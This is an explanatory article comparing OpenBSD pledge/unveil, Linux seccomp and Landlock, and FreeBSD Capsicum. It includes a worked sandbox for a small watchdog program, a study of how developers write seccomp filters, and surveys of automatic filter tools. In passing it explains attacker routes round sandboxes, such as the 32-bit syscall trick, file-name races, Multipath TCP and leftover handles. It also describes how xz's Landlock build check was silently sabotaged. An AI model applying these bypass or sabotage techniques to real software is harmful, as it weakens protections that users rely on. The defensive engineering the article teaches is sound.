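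In December 2019 isopenbsdsecu.re searched OpenBSD's source code and found 29 pledges, in 20 programs, that combine network access with writing or creating files. An attacker who takes over such a program can download a file and save it, or alter the user's files on instructions from outside. But the search overstates the problem because it looked only at pledge calls, and some of these programs also use unveil to limit which files they can reach. Beck had listed `ftp`, `spamd` and `bgpctl` among the programs using unveil a year earlier. Finer promises could not separate the two powers in `ftp` anyway, because its job is to save what arrives over the network. Developers are still adding unveil to programs that lack it. According to OpenBSD's *-current Changelog*, since the latest release they have added it to `npppd`, which handles remote network connections.

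### Changing the vocabulary in 2026

Once programs depend on a promise, changing or removing it is difficult. The promise `tmppath` let a process create, read and write files only in `/tmp`, the directory for temporary files. According to the March change log of OpenBSD (2026), de Raadt and Beck invented unveil because developers had struggled and failed to extend `tmppath` to other directories. Unveil was so different that it could not simply incorporate the old promise, and removing `tmppath` looked complicated, so they left it in place for years.

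A bug report prompted the developers to revisit `tmppath`. Within two weeks they removed it from the programs in OpenBSD itself and fixed 18 outside packages. Most of these programs now unveil `/tmp` with `rwc`, often make the rest of the file system readable, and pledge `rpath wpath cpath`. The new pledge string permits much more than the old one, so the protection depends on the unveil calls. If a developer updated the string but forgot to call unveil, the program would still work normally but could write to any of its user's files.

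De Raadt found no way to make the old `tmppath` promise behave correctly under the new arrangement, so a pledge that contains it now fails as invalid. A program that checks the result will normally stop, but one that ignores it will keep running without the limits it asked for. The developers also sent the change to users of the two existing releases, and bluhm (2026), in *OpenBSD Errata*, warned them that they might have to update some packages before using the new kernel. This change may be why the kernel rejected the Firefox helpers' pledges that April, since a leftover `tmppath` produces the same error.

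The second change concerned files that the C library needs to read for a program. A program that prints the local time needs time zone data, and one that looks up a server's name needs the list of name servers, even if it has given up opening files. The kernel used to make an exception for these paths and let any code in the process open them. Version 7.9, released in May, replaced this exception with a system call reserved for the library, `__pledge_open`. According to the release announcement from OpenBSD (2026), the process can only read through the handles this call returns and cannot pass them to another process. An attacker inside the process might still get the library to make the call, but would gain little beyond reading a few system files.

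Programs that had relied on the old exception to open such files themselves had to change. The same release fixes `dig`, a name lookup tool, which had been opening the list of name servers directly.

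## Writing the limits with seccomp, Landlock and Capsicum

On Linux, the watchdog's developer has to combine two mechanisms because there is no single pair of calls like pledge and unveil. Seccomp limits the system calls a process can make, and Landlock limits the files and network ports it can reach. On FreeBSD, once a process has restricted itself with Capsicum, it can reach files and connections only through the handles it already holds.

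### How a seccomp filter works

A seccomp filter is a small program that the developer includes in the main one and passes to the kernel during setup. From then on, the kernel runs the filter on every system call before carrying the call out. The filter's input is a short record of numbers: the number of the system call, a code for the processor architecture, and the call's arguments exactly as the process supplied them. The filter can load one of these numbers, compare it with a constant and jump ahead depending on the result. It ends by returning a value, usually one of these four:

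- **Allow:** the kernel carries out the call.
- **Error:** the kernel skips the call and returns an error code that the developer chose.
- **Trap:** the kernel skips the call and sends the process a signal. The program can handle the signal with its own code, for example to report which call it attempted.
- **Kill:** the kernel ends the process at once.

Part of a filter for the watchdog might work like this:

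```
load the architecture
    if it is not x86-64, kill
load the system call number
    if it is 0 (read), allow
    if it is 42 (connect), allow
    if it is 1 (write), go to A
    otherwise, kill
A:  load the first argument
    if it is 3, allow
    otherwise, return an error
```

The first argument of `write` is the number of a file handle. If the watchdog's log has handle 3, this filter lets the watchdog write to its log and to no other open file. But the filter checks only the number, not which file it refers to. If the filter also let the watchdog close and open files, an attacker could close handle 3 and open another file, which might get number 3 because the kernel assigns the lowest free number. The rule is therefore reliable only if the program can no longer open files.

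The most serious mistake, according to the Linux kernel documentation, is leaving out the architecture check. A 64-bit Intel or AMD machine usually also accepts system calls in the older 32-bit format, which numbers them differently. Call 11 releases memory in the 64-bit format, which nearly every program needs to do, but it starts another program in the 32-bit format. If the watchdog's filter allowed call 11 without checking the architecture, an attacker could switch formats and use it to start a command shell.

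A process can add more filters later if its existing filters still allow the system call that installs them. The kernel then runs all the filters and applies the strictest result.

### Why a filter cannot check a file name

A filter receives only the memory address of a file's name, and it has no instruction for reading the name stored there. The kernel's developers left that instruction out deliberately, because a filter that could read names would be easy to trick. An attacker who controlled the watchdog could do it with two threads:

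1. The first thread makes a call to open `/var/log/watchdog/current`.
2. The filter reads the name and allows the call.
3. Before the kernel reads the name for itself, the second thread replaces it with the path of the user's private keys.
4. The kernel opens the keys.

Security researchers call this a race between check and use. Seccomp filters avoid it because they check only numbers that the kernel has already copied and the process can no longer change. They cannot read anything a process passes through memory, including a server's address, so a filter can forbid `connect` altogether but cannot permit connections to only one server.

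Linux has a way around this restriction. A filter can return a value that hands the call to a supervisor, a separate process that can read the caller's memory. Programs that manage containers use this to intercept calls such as the one that attaches a disk. But reading the caller's memory reintroduces the race, so the documentation advises supervisors to copy the arguments into their own memory before deciding. The supervisor can then open the file itself and place the handle in the process, so the kernel never reads the file's name from the process's memory. With a supervisor, the limit is no longer purely self-imposed, because another process makes the decisions.

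### "Isn't a sandbox"

The kernel's developers write that "system call filtering isn't a sandbox" and describe it as a tool for people who build sandboxes. It is meant to reduce the amount of kernel code that an attacker can reach. For example, a filter that allows 40 of the roughly 400 system calls blocks access to the kernel code behind the others.

The filter has much less control over how a process uses the 40 calls that remain. The watchdog has to open files and send data. A filter that blocks nine tenths of the system calls but permits both of these actions cannot stop the watchdog from opening the user's private keys and sending them to a stranger. The documentation recommends combining filters with other mechanisms, such as Linux security modules, for rules about files and the flow of information. Landlock is one of these modules.

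### no_new_privs

An ordinary process must turn on an attribute named `no_new_privs` before it can install a filter. If a process with `no_new_privs` starts a program such as `sudo`, which normally runs as root no matter who starts it, the program runs without the extra rights. The process cannot turn the attribute off, and every process it starts inherits the attribute.

Without this requirement, an attacker could use a filter to make a privileged program misbehave. A filter can skip a call and return 0, the code for success, so a program that tried to switch from root to a weaker account would keep running as root with no sign that the switch had failed.

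The attribute only stops a process from gaining rights by starting a program. It doesn't remove any rights the process already has, so a root process that turns it on is still root.

Under both seccomp and Landlock, a process with administrator rights can limit itself without setting `no_new_privs`. Salaün considers this risky, because privileged programs that the process starts would then run under restrictions they may not be designed for.

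### Landlock in three steps

Landlock can tell one file from another because its check comes later in the call than seccomp's, once the kernel has worked out which file the name leads to. A process restricts itself in three steps:

1. It creates a rule set and declares which rights the set handles, such as reading files, deleting files or connecting to TCP ports.
2. It adds rules that allow some of these rights for a particular file, for a directory and everything beneath it, or for a port.
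3. It applies the rule set to itself. From then on, the kernel denies every handled right that no rule allows.

Landlock doesn't restrict a right that the developer leaves out of the first step, except for moving files between directories, which it always denies unless a rule allows it. If the watchdog's developer declares only reading and writing, then adds a rule for the log directory, the watchdog can still delete any file that its user can delete. Salaün chose this design so that a system update would not break programs. When a new kernel can restrict another kind of action, existing programs can still take that action until their developers add it to the list, so they get no new protection from the update.

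A rule refers to an open handle, not to a name. If the watchdog had a rule only for its current log and then renamed that file, the rule would still apply to the old file and would not cover the new one. So the developer attaches the rule to the log directory.

Within one rule set, the kernel allows an access if any rule along the path grants it, so a rule for a subdirectory cannot take away what a rule for its parent grants. Unlike with unveil, a developer therefore can't allow access to a home directory but exclude the folder with the private keys. Salaün recommends attaching rules as deep in the tree as possible. In his example, making `~/doc/` readable and `~/tmp/` writable is better than making all of `~/` readable and `~/tmp/` writable.

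A process can apply a second rule set later, for example when it finishes one stage of its work. The kernel then permits an access only if every rule set permits it. At most 16 sets can apply to a process, including those it inherits. A program that starts other programs, such as a command shell, should not use several, because those programs may need to add their own.

Because files opened during setup stay usable, the watchdog can keep writing to its open log even if no rule covers that file. Permission to empty a file is also tied to the handle, so a process can have two handles to the same log but be able to empty it through only one. If the process passes a handle to another process, the handle's permissions go with it.

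Landlock still cannot restrict some actions, including changing a file's permissions, owner or timestamps, and looking up details such as its size. An attacker who controlled the watchdog could therefore make the user's private keys readable to every other account on the machine, even though he could not read them himself.

### Five new versions in 2026

The first version of Landlock's interface covered only files. Versions 2 to 7 added controls for moving files between directories, emptying files, TCP ports, commands to devices, signals and some local connections, and logging. Salaün and other developers added five more versions in 2026:

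| Version | Linux release | What it adds |
|---|---|---|
| 8 | 7.0 | Applying a rule set to all threads at once |
| 9 | 7.1 | Limits on connecting to local services through socket files |
| 10 | 7.2 | Limits on UDP ports |
| 11 | 7.3 | Turning on `no_new_privs` in the same step as the rules |
| 12 | 7.4 (expected) | Limits on capabilities and namespaces |

Version 8 closes the gap that let an attacker act through another thread in the same process. Salaün (2026), in *[GIT PULL] Landlock update for v7.0-rc1* compares the fix to an existing seccomp option. Even on a current kernel, the fix takes effect only if the program passes a flag when it restricts itself.

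Before version 11, a program had to turn on `no_new_privs` and then apply its rules in a second call. If that call failed, the program had given up the ability to gain new privileges but had no sandbox. With the new flag, either both changes take effect or neither does.

Version 12 deals with a longer-standing problem. Linux divides root's power into pieces called capabilities, such as the power to set the clock. An ordinary process has none, but on many systems it can create a user namespace, a private set of accounts in which the kernel gives it every capability. It still cannot set the real clock, but it can reach kernel code otherwise reserved for root. Salaün (2026), in *[PATCH v2 0/9] Landlock*, lists seven vulnerabilities that attackers could exploit only in this way, three of them from 2026. Advisories for those three recommended preventing ordinary users from creating user namespaces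 until a fix was in place.

Neither `no_new_privs` nor seccomp fully solves this. `no_new_privs` has no effect because the process gains the capabilities without starting a privileged program. A seccomp filter can block the older calls that create namespaces, but the newer `clone3` passes its options in memory, where the filter can't read them. The filter can therefore only allow or block all uses of `clone3`, including those that start ordinary threads.

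Version 12 of Landlock lets a process list the capabilities and the types of namespace it may use, and the kernel denies the rest. Salaün points out that restricting only one of the two leaves a way to get around the restriction. Once a process restricts either category, later kernels also deny any new capabilities or namespace types they add to that category. This is stricter than Landlock's treatment of files, where new access rights stay allowed until the developer declares them.

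Developers may be confused because denied capabilities are still listed when a process looks up its own capabilities, and the denial becomes apparent only when the process tries to use one. According to the Linux kernel's change log, Salaün kept the list unchanged because other security modules do the same. He added these limits on 20 October 2026, so they should first appear in Linux 7.4. That version was still in testing in November, when Torvalds (2026) asked developers in *Linux 7.4-rc2* to keep trying it out.

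### The watchdog on Linux

The outline below shortens the names of Landlock's constants. The outline's helper functions build each rule and stop the program if the kernel rejects one. The watchdog tests port 443, the usual port for secure websites.

```c
/* Setup phase */
read_settings("/etc/watchdog.conf");
open_log("/var/log/watchdog/current");

/* Landlock: which files and ports */
int rules = new_rules(ALL_FILE_RIGHTS, ALL_NETWORK_RIGHTS);
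allow_path(rules, "/var/log/watchdog",
           READ_FILE | WRITE_FILE | TRUNCATE | MAKE_REG | REMOVE_FILE);
allow_lookup_files(rules);                   /* /etc/hosts and others */
allow_port(rules, 443, CONNECT_TCP);         /* the test itself */
allow_port(rules, 53, CONNECT_TCP | CONNECT_SEND_UDP);  /* lookups */
allow_port(rules, 0, BIND_UDP);              /* local port for lookups */
restrict_self(rules, ALL_THREADS | NO_NEW_PRIVS);

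/* seccomp: which system calls */
filter_t filter = new_filter(KILL_PROCESS);
allow_calls(filter, "read write openat close fstat rename");
allow_calls(filter, "connect sendto recvfrom poll");
allow_calls(filter, "clock_gettime clock_nanosleep exit_group");
allow_sockets(filter, ORDINARY_TCP_AND_UDP);
install(filter);

/* Working phase */
check_port_every_minute();
```

The watchdog applies Landlock before the seccomp filter because the filter would otherwise have to permit Landlock's own system calls. To rename a log, even within the same directory, the watchdog needs both `REMOVE_FILE` and `MAKE_REG`, the right to create ordinary files. The rule for port 0 lets the kernel choose a local port for each name lookup, and without it lookups over UDP would fail.

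A real list of system calls would be longer, since memory allocation and name lookup also make system calls. It would also have to include calls that the developer may never observe. On most machines, a process can read the clock without a system call, using data that the kernel shares with it, but on others the same code falls back to the `clock_gettime` system call. If the list left that call out, the watchdog would run well on the developer's machine, but the kernel would kill it on a customer's machine that uses the fallback.

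`allow_sockets` fills a gap in Landlock, whose TCP rules do not apply to related protocols such as Multipath TCP. Multipath TCP can use several network paths at once, and it falls back to ordinary TCP when the server doesn't support it. With Landlock alone, an attacker could therefore use a Multipath TCP socket to connect to any port on any server. The seccomp filter can check the protocol because a process passes the protocol number directly when it creates a socket.

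If an attacker takes over the watchdog, the two mechanisms stop different things:

| What the attacker tries | seccomp | Landlock |
|---|---|---|
| Read the user's private keys | Allows it, since `openat` is on the list | Denies it |
| Make the keys readable to other accounts | Kills the watchdog | Cannot restrict it |
| Start a command shell | Kills the watchdog | Denies it |
| Connect to another machine on port 22 | Allows it, since `connect` is on the list | Denies it |
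| Do the same over Multipath TCP | Blocks the socket | Does not cover it |
| Exploit a bug in a rarely used system call | Kills the watchdog | Usually does not cover it |
| Delete the old logs | Kills the watchdog if he uses `unlink` | Allows it |
| Overwrite the old logs | Allows it | Allows it |
| Send the watchdog's memory to a server on port 443 | Allows it | Allows it |

The result is much longer than the three calls on OpenBSD, and a change in the C library can break it. But it restricts the network more tightly than the `inet` promise, since an attacker can connect only to ports 443 and 53 and can't run a server. Neither system can limit the attacker to the one machine the watchdog is supposed to test.

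### Capsicum

With Capsicum, a process gives up the use of global names, which mean the same thing to every process. Examples are full file paths, process numbers and network addresses. The process calls `cap_enter` to enter FreeBSD's capability mode. According to FreeBSD's *CAP_ENTER(2)*, it can then make only system calls that work on handles it holds or that read a limited amount of general system information. It cannot leave this mode, and its children start in it.

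In Capsicum, a capability is a handle with a list of permitted operations. Linux capabilities, which divide root's power, are unrelated. The developer can shorten the list for each handle separately. In an example from FreeBSD, a process keeps the right to read and write a file but loses the right to change its permissions. The watchdog's developer could similarly allow new entries in the log but not the call that empties the file.

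A handle for a directory lets the process open and rename files beneath that directory and nowhere else. The watchdog could open its log directory during setup, enter capability mode and keep rotating its logs.

The watchdog's connections are harder to handle because it has to make a new one every minute, and the kernel blocks each attempt because an address is a global name. The watchdog would need a helper process outside capability mode to make each connection and pass back the open socket. FreeBSD's libcasper library has ready-made helpers for connections and name lookup. Dividing the program this way takes more work, but the developer could also use the helper to limit the watchdog to one server, which neither the OpenBSD version nor the Linux version can do.

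Under Capsicum, a process's open handles determine what it can reach. This makes `cap_enter` simple to call, and a program that already works through handles, as gmid did, may need little else. But the source code doesn't list what the process can still reach. If the watchdog entered capability mode with a handle for the user's home directory still open, an attacker could use that handle to open the private keys. The developer therefore has to account for every open handle, including any that the watchdog inherited from the program that started it.

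### The four mechanisms compared

| | pledge with unveil | seccomp | Landlock | Capsicum |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| **What it restricts** | Groups of operations, and file paths | System calls | Files, TCP and UDP ports, signals, some local connections and, from version 12, capabilities and namespaces | All access by global name, and operations on each handle |
| **How finely** | About three dozen groups, and single files | Single calls and numeric arguments, but not file names or server addresses | Single files and ports, but not single servers | Single handles, each with its own rights |
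| **Inheritance** | Copies of the process keep both limits. New programs start without either, but the parent can set execpromises for pledge | Copies and new programs keep the filter | Copies and new programs keep the rules. Threads that are already running need a flag | Copies and new programs stay in capability mode |
| **On a violation** | pledge usually kills the process, and unveil returns an error | The developer chooses, for example an error or a kill | The call returns an error | The call normally returns an error |
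| **Typical mistake** | Keeping `exec` and forgetting that new programs start without limits | Not checking the architecture | Not declaring a right, which leaves it unrestricted | Entering capability mode with a powerful handle still open |

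## Working out what the program needs

The watchdog's developer can't finish the seccomp filter without knowing which system calls the watchdog makes. These calls rarely appear in its source code, because the C library makes most of them.

If the developer's list lacks a call that the watchdog needs, the watchdog may crash months later. Including a call that the watchdog never needs benefits only an attacker. Lists tend to become too long because users report crashes, but nobody reports unneeded calls.

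### Reading, recording and automatic analysis

A developer can find rare actions by reading the code. The statement that renames the log is easy to spot, even if the watchdog runs it only once a month. The system calls that a library function makes are harder to identify. For example, when a program opens a file for appending, the library makes one call to open it and another, `lseek`, to move to its end. To look up a file's size, the library may use `fstat`, `newfstatat` or another variant, depending on its version and the processor.

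`strace`, a standard Linux tool, records the exact name of every system call a program makes as it runs, along with details such as file paths, which help in writing Landlock rules. But it shows only the calls made during that run. According to *B-Side* (2024), a paper on automatic analysis, recordings always risk missing calls because it is so hard to make a program run all of its code.

A recording also includes calls that the program won't need once it has limited itself. Rossi, Abbadini and colleagues explain in *SysComb* (2026) that `strace` starts before the program does. It therefore records `execve`, the call that launches the program, and then all the calls that load libraries and set up memory.

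In automatic analysis, a tool examines the source or machine code without running it. The tool builds a call graph, a map of which functions each function can call, and follows it from the start of the program through the libraries to the system calls. Programs often call whichever function a variable currently points to, and the tool usually can't work out which function that will be, so it has to include every plausible one.

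In *Temporal System Call Specialization for Attack Surface Reduction*, Ghavamnia, Palit and colleagues examine an indirect call in the Apache web server. A standard analysis reported 136 possible targets for the call, but the researchers checked by hand and found that only seven could run. Elsewhere in Apache, a false target led to a function that starts other programs, so the filter would have had to allow `execve` unnecessarily.

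*Shrinking the Kernel Attack Surface Through Static and Dynamic Syscall Limitation* (Zhan, Yu and colleagues, 2025) compared the two kinds of list for 100 common Linux programs. Automatic analysis allowed an average of 87 system calls per program. When the researchers ran the programs with varied inputs, they recorded an average of 14. The programs' real needs lie somewhere between these figures, but neither method shows where.

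### Seven developers and a watchdog

Alhindi and Hallett (2025), in *Playing in the Sandbox*, studied how developers draw up such a list. They recruited seven men who had used seccomp before, paid each about $250, and gave them an hour to restrict a 115-line C watchdog. The developers could change the program and consult anything they liked. The researchers watched their screens and asked them to think aloud.

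This watchdog is simpler than the one described so far. It never looks up a name or reads a file. It connects to port 22 on a fixed address every two seconds, adds the result to a log, and renames the log once it exceeds 200 bytes. Six of the seven developers produced a working filter, and all six used an allow list.

| Developer | Calls allowed | Lines of code added | How he drew up the list |
|---|---|---|---|
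| 1 | 9 | 19 | Made a recording and matched each call to the program |
| 2 | 11 | 43 | Read the code, then corrected his list from a recording |
| 3 | 22 | 298 | Matched a recording to the program, then added variants for other systems |
| 4 | No working filter | 25 | Copied an example that he could not follow |
| 5 | 26 | 57 | Gave a recording to ChatGPT |
| 6 | 11 | 58 | Made a recording and matched each call to the program |
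| 7 | 27 | 45 | Copied a recording, then added calls it had missed |

The watchdog's main loop needs nine calls, and all six working filters allowed them. `read` isn't among the nine, because this watchdog only writes. An attacker limited to these calls could overwrite or rename the user's files and send out whatever was in the watchdog's memory, but couldn't read the user's private keys.

Developers 5 and 7 trusted the `strace` recording and allowed 15 calls that the watchdog didn't need. These included `mmap`, which an attacker could use to load the keys into memory and read them, and `execve`, which could start another program. The new program would inherit the filter, but it could probably still load, because the filter allowed the recorded start-up calls.

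The same recording was also too short. An empty log takes seven or eight checks, or about 15 seconds, to pass 200 bytes. Developer 5's first recording ended before the watchdog renamed the log, so the filter that ChatGPT wrote from it did not allow `rename`, and the kernel killed the watchdog after a few rounds. He found the cause only after the researchers gave him a hint.

An earlier filter from ChatGPT allowed everything by default, which he noticed and corrected himself. He had chosen ChatGPT to save time but took longer than anyone else who got a filter working. A better model might have avoided the wrong default, but it could not have identified the rename from a recording that didn't contain it.

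Developers 1 and 5 also forgot `exit_group`, the call that ends a program. The watchdog uses this call only when something goes wrong or the user stops the watchdog, and both men had concentrated on the main loop. The mistake did little damage here, since the kernel would kill a program that was about to end anyway, but the kill could look like an attack.

Developer 7's watchdog died once while trying to make a call named `restart_syscall`, which appears nowhere in its source. The kernel uses this call to resume an interrupted sleep. He couldn't reproduce the crash and never found the cause. Developer 3 worried about overlooking a call like this and left his program running through the rest of the interview to see whether it would fail.

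Only developer 2 limited the arguments of system calls. He allowed ordinary internet connections but not connections to local services, and let the watchdog write only short messages, and only to the screen and its two logs. The connection rule is sound. The log rule is weaker than it looks, because this watchdog reopens its logs on every round, so an attacker could open another file under the same handle number. When developer 2 first tested his rules, a forbidden write succeeded because he had forgotten to switch the filter on.

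None of the seven developers changed the program to open files and sockets before the main loop, which could have removed the need for some of the nine calls. Developer 2 had about half an hour left and spent it tidying his code. He said he would design for maximum security from the start, but would not rewrite a whole program just to use seccomp properly.

Afterwards, the researchers asked the developers to design their ideal sandbox. Some wanted to keep working with system calls, while others wanted broader groups of operations, similar to pledge's promises. Developer 6 wanted to write each function's permissions next to the function, so that anyone changing the code would see them.

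With only seven participants, the study can't show how common any of these mistakes is, and Alhindi and Hallett don't claim it does. The developers worked under observation on an unfamiliar program, and some might have done better with more time. But the researchers had turned away four volunteers who had never used seccomp, so the participants knew more about it than most programmers do. They all restricted the same short program, so the range from 9 to 27 calls came from their methods and judgement. The three who matched every recorded call to the code and added nothing for other systems ended up with 9 or 11.

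### How many programs bind themselves

In an earlier survey, Alhindi and Hallett searched the source code of every package they could download for four operating systems. The data date from April to August 2023.

| System | Packages that bind themselves | Processes with limits after startup |
|---|---|---|
| Debian | 406 of 59,893 (0.68%) | 5 of 120 |
| Fedora | 396 of 63,706 (0.62%) | 16 of 137 |
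| OpenBSD | 114 of 7,700 (1.48%) | 33 of 36 |
| FreeBSD | 43 of 30,763 (0.14%) | 3 of 47 |

The package shares are rough because they include packages that contain only documentation, and the search covered mainly C and C++ code. Of the 406 packages counted for Debian, 97 were versions of Firefox, many differing only in language. Many more packages depend on a program that limits itself, up to 45% on FreeBSD, but this is little evidence of their own safety. For example, the survey counted one terminal program in this group because a long chain of dependencies led to the remote login tool OpenSSH.

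OpenBSD's two figures differ so much because its developers write most of the programs that run at startup and can restrict them as they write them. Packages come from outside developers, and only 1.48% of them used pledge or unveil, even though both calls are easy to write. Developers still have to work out what a program needs and reorganise it.

No package used Landlock to restrict itself. The only uses were in kernel tests and a sample program. Landlock was then two years old and could not yet limit network connections, so the result is weak evidence about its use today.

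About 80% of the Linux packages that used seccomp also checked system call arguments, compared with one developer in seven in the usability study. The package figure is inflated because it includes multiple copies of the same program, but long-term maintainers also have more reason to refine a filter than study participants with an hour to work on it.

The network tool `arping` shows what this extra precision can achieve. On OpenBSD it pledges `stdio` and `tty`, which covers the terminal, and its unveil call leaves the whole file system visible. Its Linux filter has a much shorter list of calls, and lets it write only to the screen and send only certain kinds of request to devices. On FreeBSD it has no limits.

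The developer of `xwallpaper`, by contrast, gained no precision by copying pledge's calls into a seccomp filter. Comments in the filter label each block of calls with the matching promise, such as `pledge: dns`, and the developer has to update the list by hand. Copying is common. Three other packages share similar filter code, and Flatpak, which distributes desktop applications, took its list of forbidden calls from an older tool. Copying a list saves work, but the list was written for the needs of a different program.

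### Filters written by tools

Developer 2 thought ordinary programmers would need automation, but he didn't know that researchers had already built several tools for this. One of them, *sysfilter* by DeMarinis, Williams-King and colleagues, works from machine code, so it needs neither the source nor the developer's help. It builds a call graph of the program and its libraries, includes every function that an indirect call might reach, and adds the resulting filter to the program. The researchers restricted 411 programs this way and ran about 38,500 tests without finding a missing system call. Of the roughly 30,000 Debian programs they also analysed, about 45% never used `execve`, and 65% never used `listen`, which a program needs to accept network connections.

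Confine applies similar analysis to containers, which package a program with the files it needs. It first runs the container to see which programs start, then analyses each one. The default filter in Docker, a widely used container system, blocks only about 50 calls because it has to suit almost any program.

Canella, Werner and colleagues (2020), in *Automating Seccomp Filter Generation for Linux Applications*, present Chestnut, a tool that works out which system calls a program needs by analysing it during compilation or from the finished machine code. In tests on 18 programs, its filters blocked an average of 86.5% of system calls when built during compilation and 82.5% when built from machine code. Users can also record the calls a program makes as it runs, then allow calls that the analysis missed or block ones that never occurred. The researchers ran a web server under a Chestnut filter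 for six months, and it handled about 100,000 requests without a violation.

These tools produce one filter for the program's whole run, including setup. Ghavamnia and colleagues avoid this with temporal specialization, which adds a stricter filter when a server begins to handle requests. Someone who knows the program has to mark that point in the source code. The method disabled 51% more of the calls that attackers' code commonly uses than earlier tools did by removing unused library code.

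*SysPart* (Rajagopalan, Kleftogiorgos and colleagues, 2023) automates that step and needs only machine code. It looks for a loop that the server enters once and then spends most of its time in. Its filters allowed 8.33% more calls on average than temporal specialization. *C2C* (Ghavamnia, Palit and Polychronakis, 2022) instead uses the program's settings to block calls that only switched-off features need.

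Automatic analysis can also miss calls. Apache can load its encryption code while running, and that code needs 14 more calls. Temporal specialization does not account for libraries loaded this way, so its filter could break encrypted connections. Chestnut's analysis of machine code missed 13 calls in the database SQLite, and the optional recording then added them.

DeMarinis and colleagues write that the list of calls their tool produces is guaranteed to be complete for any input. But when Canella and colleagues used the tool on the Redis database, it found only 12 calls, while Redis made at least 35 in their tests. The tool had dropped the program's main function. The comparison is somewhat unfair, because Canella and colleagues had compiled Redis in a form that the tool wasn't designed to handle.

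A program's filter also applies to any programs it starts, so analyzing the first program alone doesn't show every call the filter must allow. For example, two commands in `git`, a tool for tracking changes to files, start a separate program to display their output. That program crashed under Chestnut's first filters because it needed calls that `git` itself did not.

### The effect on kernel flaws

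Researchers often judge a filter by which known kernel flaws it would stop an attacker from exploiting. Canella and colleagues collected 175 flaws reported since 2003 and looked up the system calls needed to exploit each one. They counted a flaw as blocked if the filter forbade any of those calls.

| Tool | What it analyses | Effect on system calls | Effect on known kernel flaws |
|---|---|---|---|
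| sysfilter | Machine code | 45% of Debian programs studied can lose `execve` | About as effective as Chestnut, on a different set of 23 |
| Chestnut | Source or machine code | Removes 82.5% to 86.5% | Blocks over 62% of 175 |
| Temporal specialization | Source code, in two phases | Disables 51% more dangerous calls than library trimming | Blocks 53 in total |
| SysPart | Machine code, in two phases | Leaves 8.33% more than temporal specialization | Blocks 36% to 78% of those tested, depending on the server |
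| C2C | Source code and settings | Removes calls needed only by unused features | Blocks 88 in total |
| sysverify | Source and machine code | Removes 74% | Blocks 87 in total, before its extra checks |
| SysComb | Recordings of each phase | Allows 21% fewer while serving than one filter for the whole run | Gives better protection than one filter against 17 of 45 |

Readers can't rank the tools by the last column, because the researchers tested them on different flaws and programs. Each total counts the flaws that a tool blocked in at least some of the programs, so the tool may block fewer in any single program.

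The share of calls removed overstates how well the filters protect. For Nginx, a popular web server, Chestnut removed 70% of system calls but blocked only 32% of the flaws. On average, it blocked about 84% of flaws for small command-line tools and 38% for larger programs. Many flaws are reached through calls that large programs need, so servers, which face the most attacks, gain the least. Blocking a flaw protects only the kernel, not the files and connections that the program can still reach.

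Recent tools are designed to narrow the gap between the calls a program might make and those it usually makes. Sysverify, by Zhan and colleagues, starts with an ordinary seccomp filter produced by automatic analysis. When the program makes a rare call for the first time, an added kernel module checks the chain of functions that led to it and refuses the call if the call graph doesn't contain that chain. Sysverify stopped 81% more flaws than Confine did. An attacker who can forge the record of function calls in the program's memory could get past this check, though the researchers consider this very difficult.

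SysComb, which Rossi and colleagues released in August 2026, records the calls a program makes in each phase separately. A developer marks the points where the program moves from one phase to the next. Recording starts after the program has loaded, so it leaves out the launch calls that misled developers 5 and 7. Once recording is finished, the kernel switches filters whenever the program reaches a marked point, with no change to the program's code.

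The researchers recorded nine servers running their test suites, then ran the same tests under the new filters without errors. But the tests exercised only about 79% of the code on average, so passing them again doesn't show that the rest works under the filters. SysComb also loses some of the simplicity of self-binding, because an administrator has to load it and, in its strictest mode, a program can regain calls when it enters a new phase. To stop an attacker from exploiting this, SysComb allows only the sequences of phases it recorded.

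In *Making (Only) the Right Calls*, Lei and Shue also make filters depend on what the program is doing, for web applications written in PHP. They object that earlier filters allow every call any part of the application might make.

For a program as small as the watchdog, a developer can combine the methods by hand. If a call appears in the automatic analysis but not in the recording, the developer has to decide whether it is rare or impossible, and the source code usually settles the question. The developer can also make rare events happen during the recording:

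- let the log grow until the watchdog renames it
- switch off the remote server so that a connection fails
- make the log unwritable so that the watchdog exits with an error
- suspend the watchdog while it is sleeping, then resume it, which triggers `restart_syscall`

The list should include only the calls recorded after the point where the watchdog will limit itself. That leaves out `execve` and the other start-up calls unless the watchdog makes them again after that point.

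## Checking that the limits are in force and stay in force

Even after the watchdog's developer has listed its permissions and added the calls that apply them, one of the limits could be missing. The watchdog would still check its port every minute and write its log, so nothing would look wrong until an attacker did something the kernel should have refused. One developer in the usability study briefly had this problem and noticed only because he tested a forbidden write.

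### How a limit goes missing without a sign

| What went wrong | What the user sees | What finds it |
|---|---|---|
| The program never makes the call that limits it | Nothing | Attempt a forbidden action |
| The kernel is too old, or someone has turned the feature off | Usually nothing, if the program carries on regardless | Ask the kernel which version it supports, and repeat the attempt on the oldest kernel in use |
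| A check during the build left the limits out | At most a line in the build log | Make the build stop if the limits are unavailable, and test the finished program |
| Another thread was already running when the program limited itself | Nothing, and the main thread passes every test | Make the attempt from each thread |
| The process holds a powerful handle from before | Nothing, and new attempts to open the file fail as they should | List the open handles |

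A kernel too old to support Landlock is easy to detect. When Landlock is on, the Linux kernel's log contains the line "landlock: Up and running". A program that asks for the Landlock version gets one error code if the kernel lacks Landlock and a different one if someone disabled it at startup, according to Salaün. In the second case, an administrator can turn Landlock back on with a setting.

Leftover handles are harder to notice, especially one that the watchdog inherited from the script that started it.

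A program can also lack one limit while its others work. When Landlock became able to restrict TCP connections, xz's developers added the new limit to `xz` but forgot `xzdec`, a smaller program that only decompresses. They corrected this in May 2024, according to the release notes from XZ Utils (2026). Until then, `xzdec` would have passed any test of its file limits but could still have opened TCP connections.

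### The sabotaged build check in xz

That omission was an honest mistake, but someone had also sabotaged xz's limits. Versions 5.6.0 and 5.6.1 contained a backdoor aimed at SSH servers, which people use to log in to remote machines. xz's maintainer, Lasse Collin, writing as Larhzu (2024), states in *xz backdoor* that a developer using the name Jia Tan created and signed both releases.

On 26 February 2024, between the two releases, Jia Tan changed how xz's build decides whether to include the Landlock limits. The build had looked for a file that describes Landlock to the compiler. After the change, it tried to compile a few lines of code that use Landlock and included the limits only if that code compiled. The new test looked more careful, and the reason given for it in a comment was that some systems have the file but lack the system calls. The release notes for 5.6.1 listed the change as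 a fix.

The test code had a full stop on a line by itself, which is not valid C, so the code never compiled and the build always treated Landlock as unavailable. sjw (2024), in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*, pointed out that this happened silently unless the person building xz had explicitly required the sandbox. Collin removed the full stop on 30 March, the day after the backdoor became public, with the comment "It never enabled it." He later reviewed Jia Tan's changes one by one and described the full stop as sabotage in his notes on the project's website, Tukaani.

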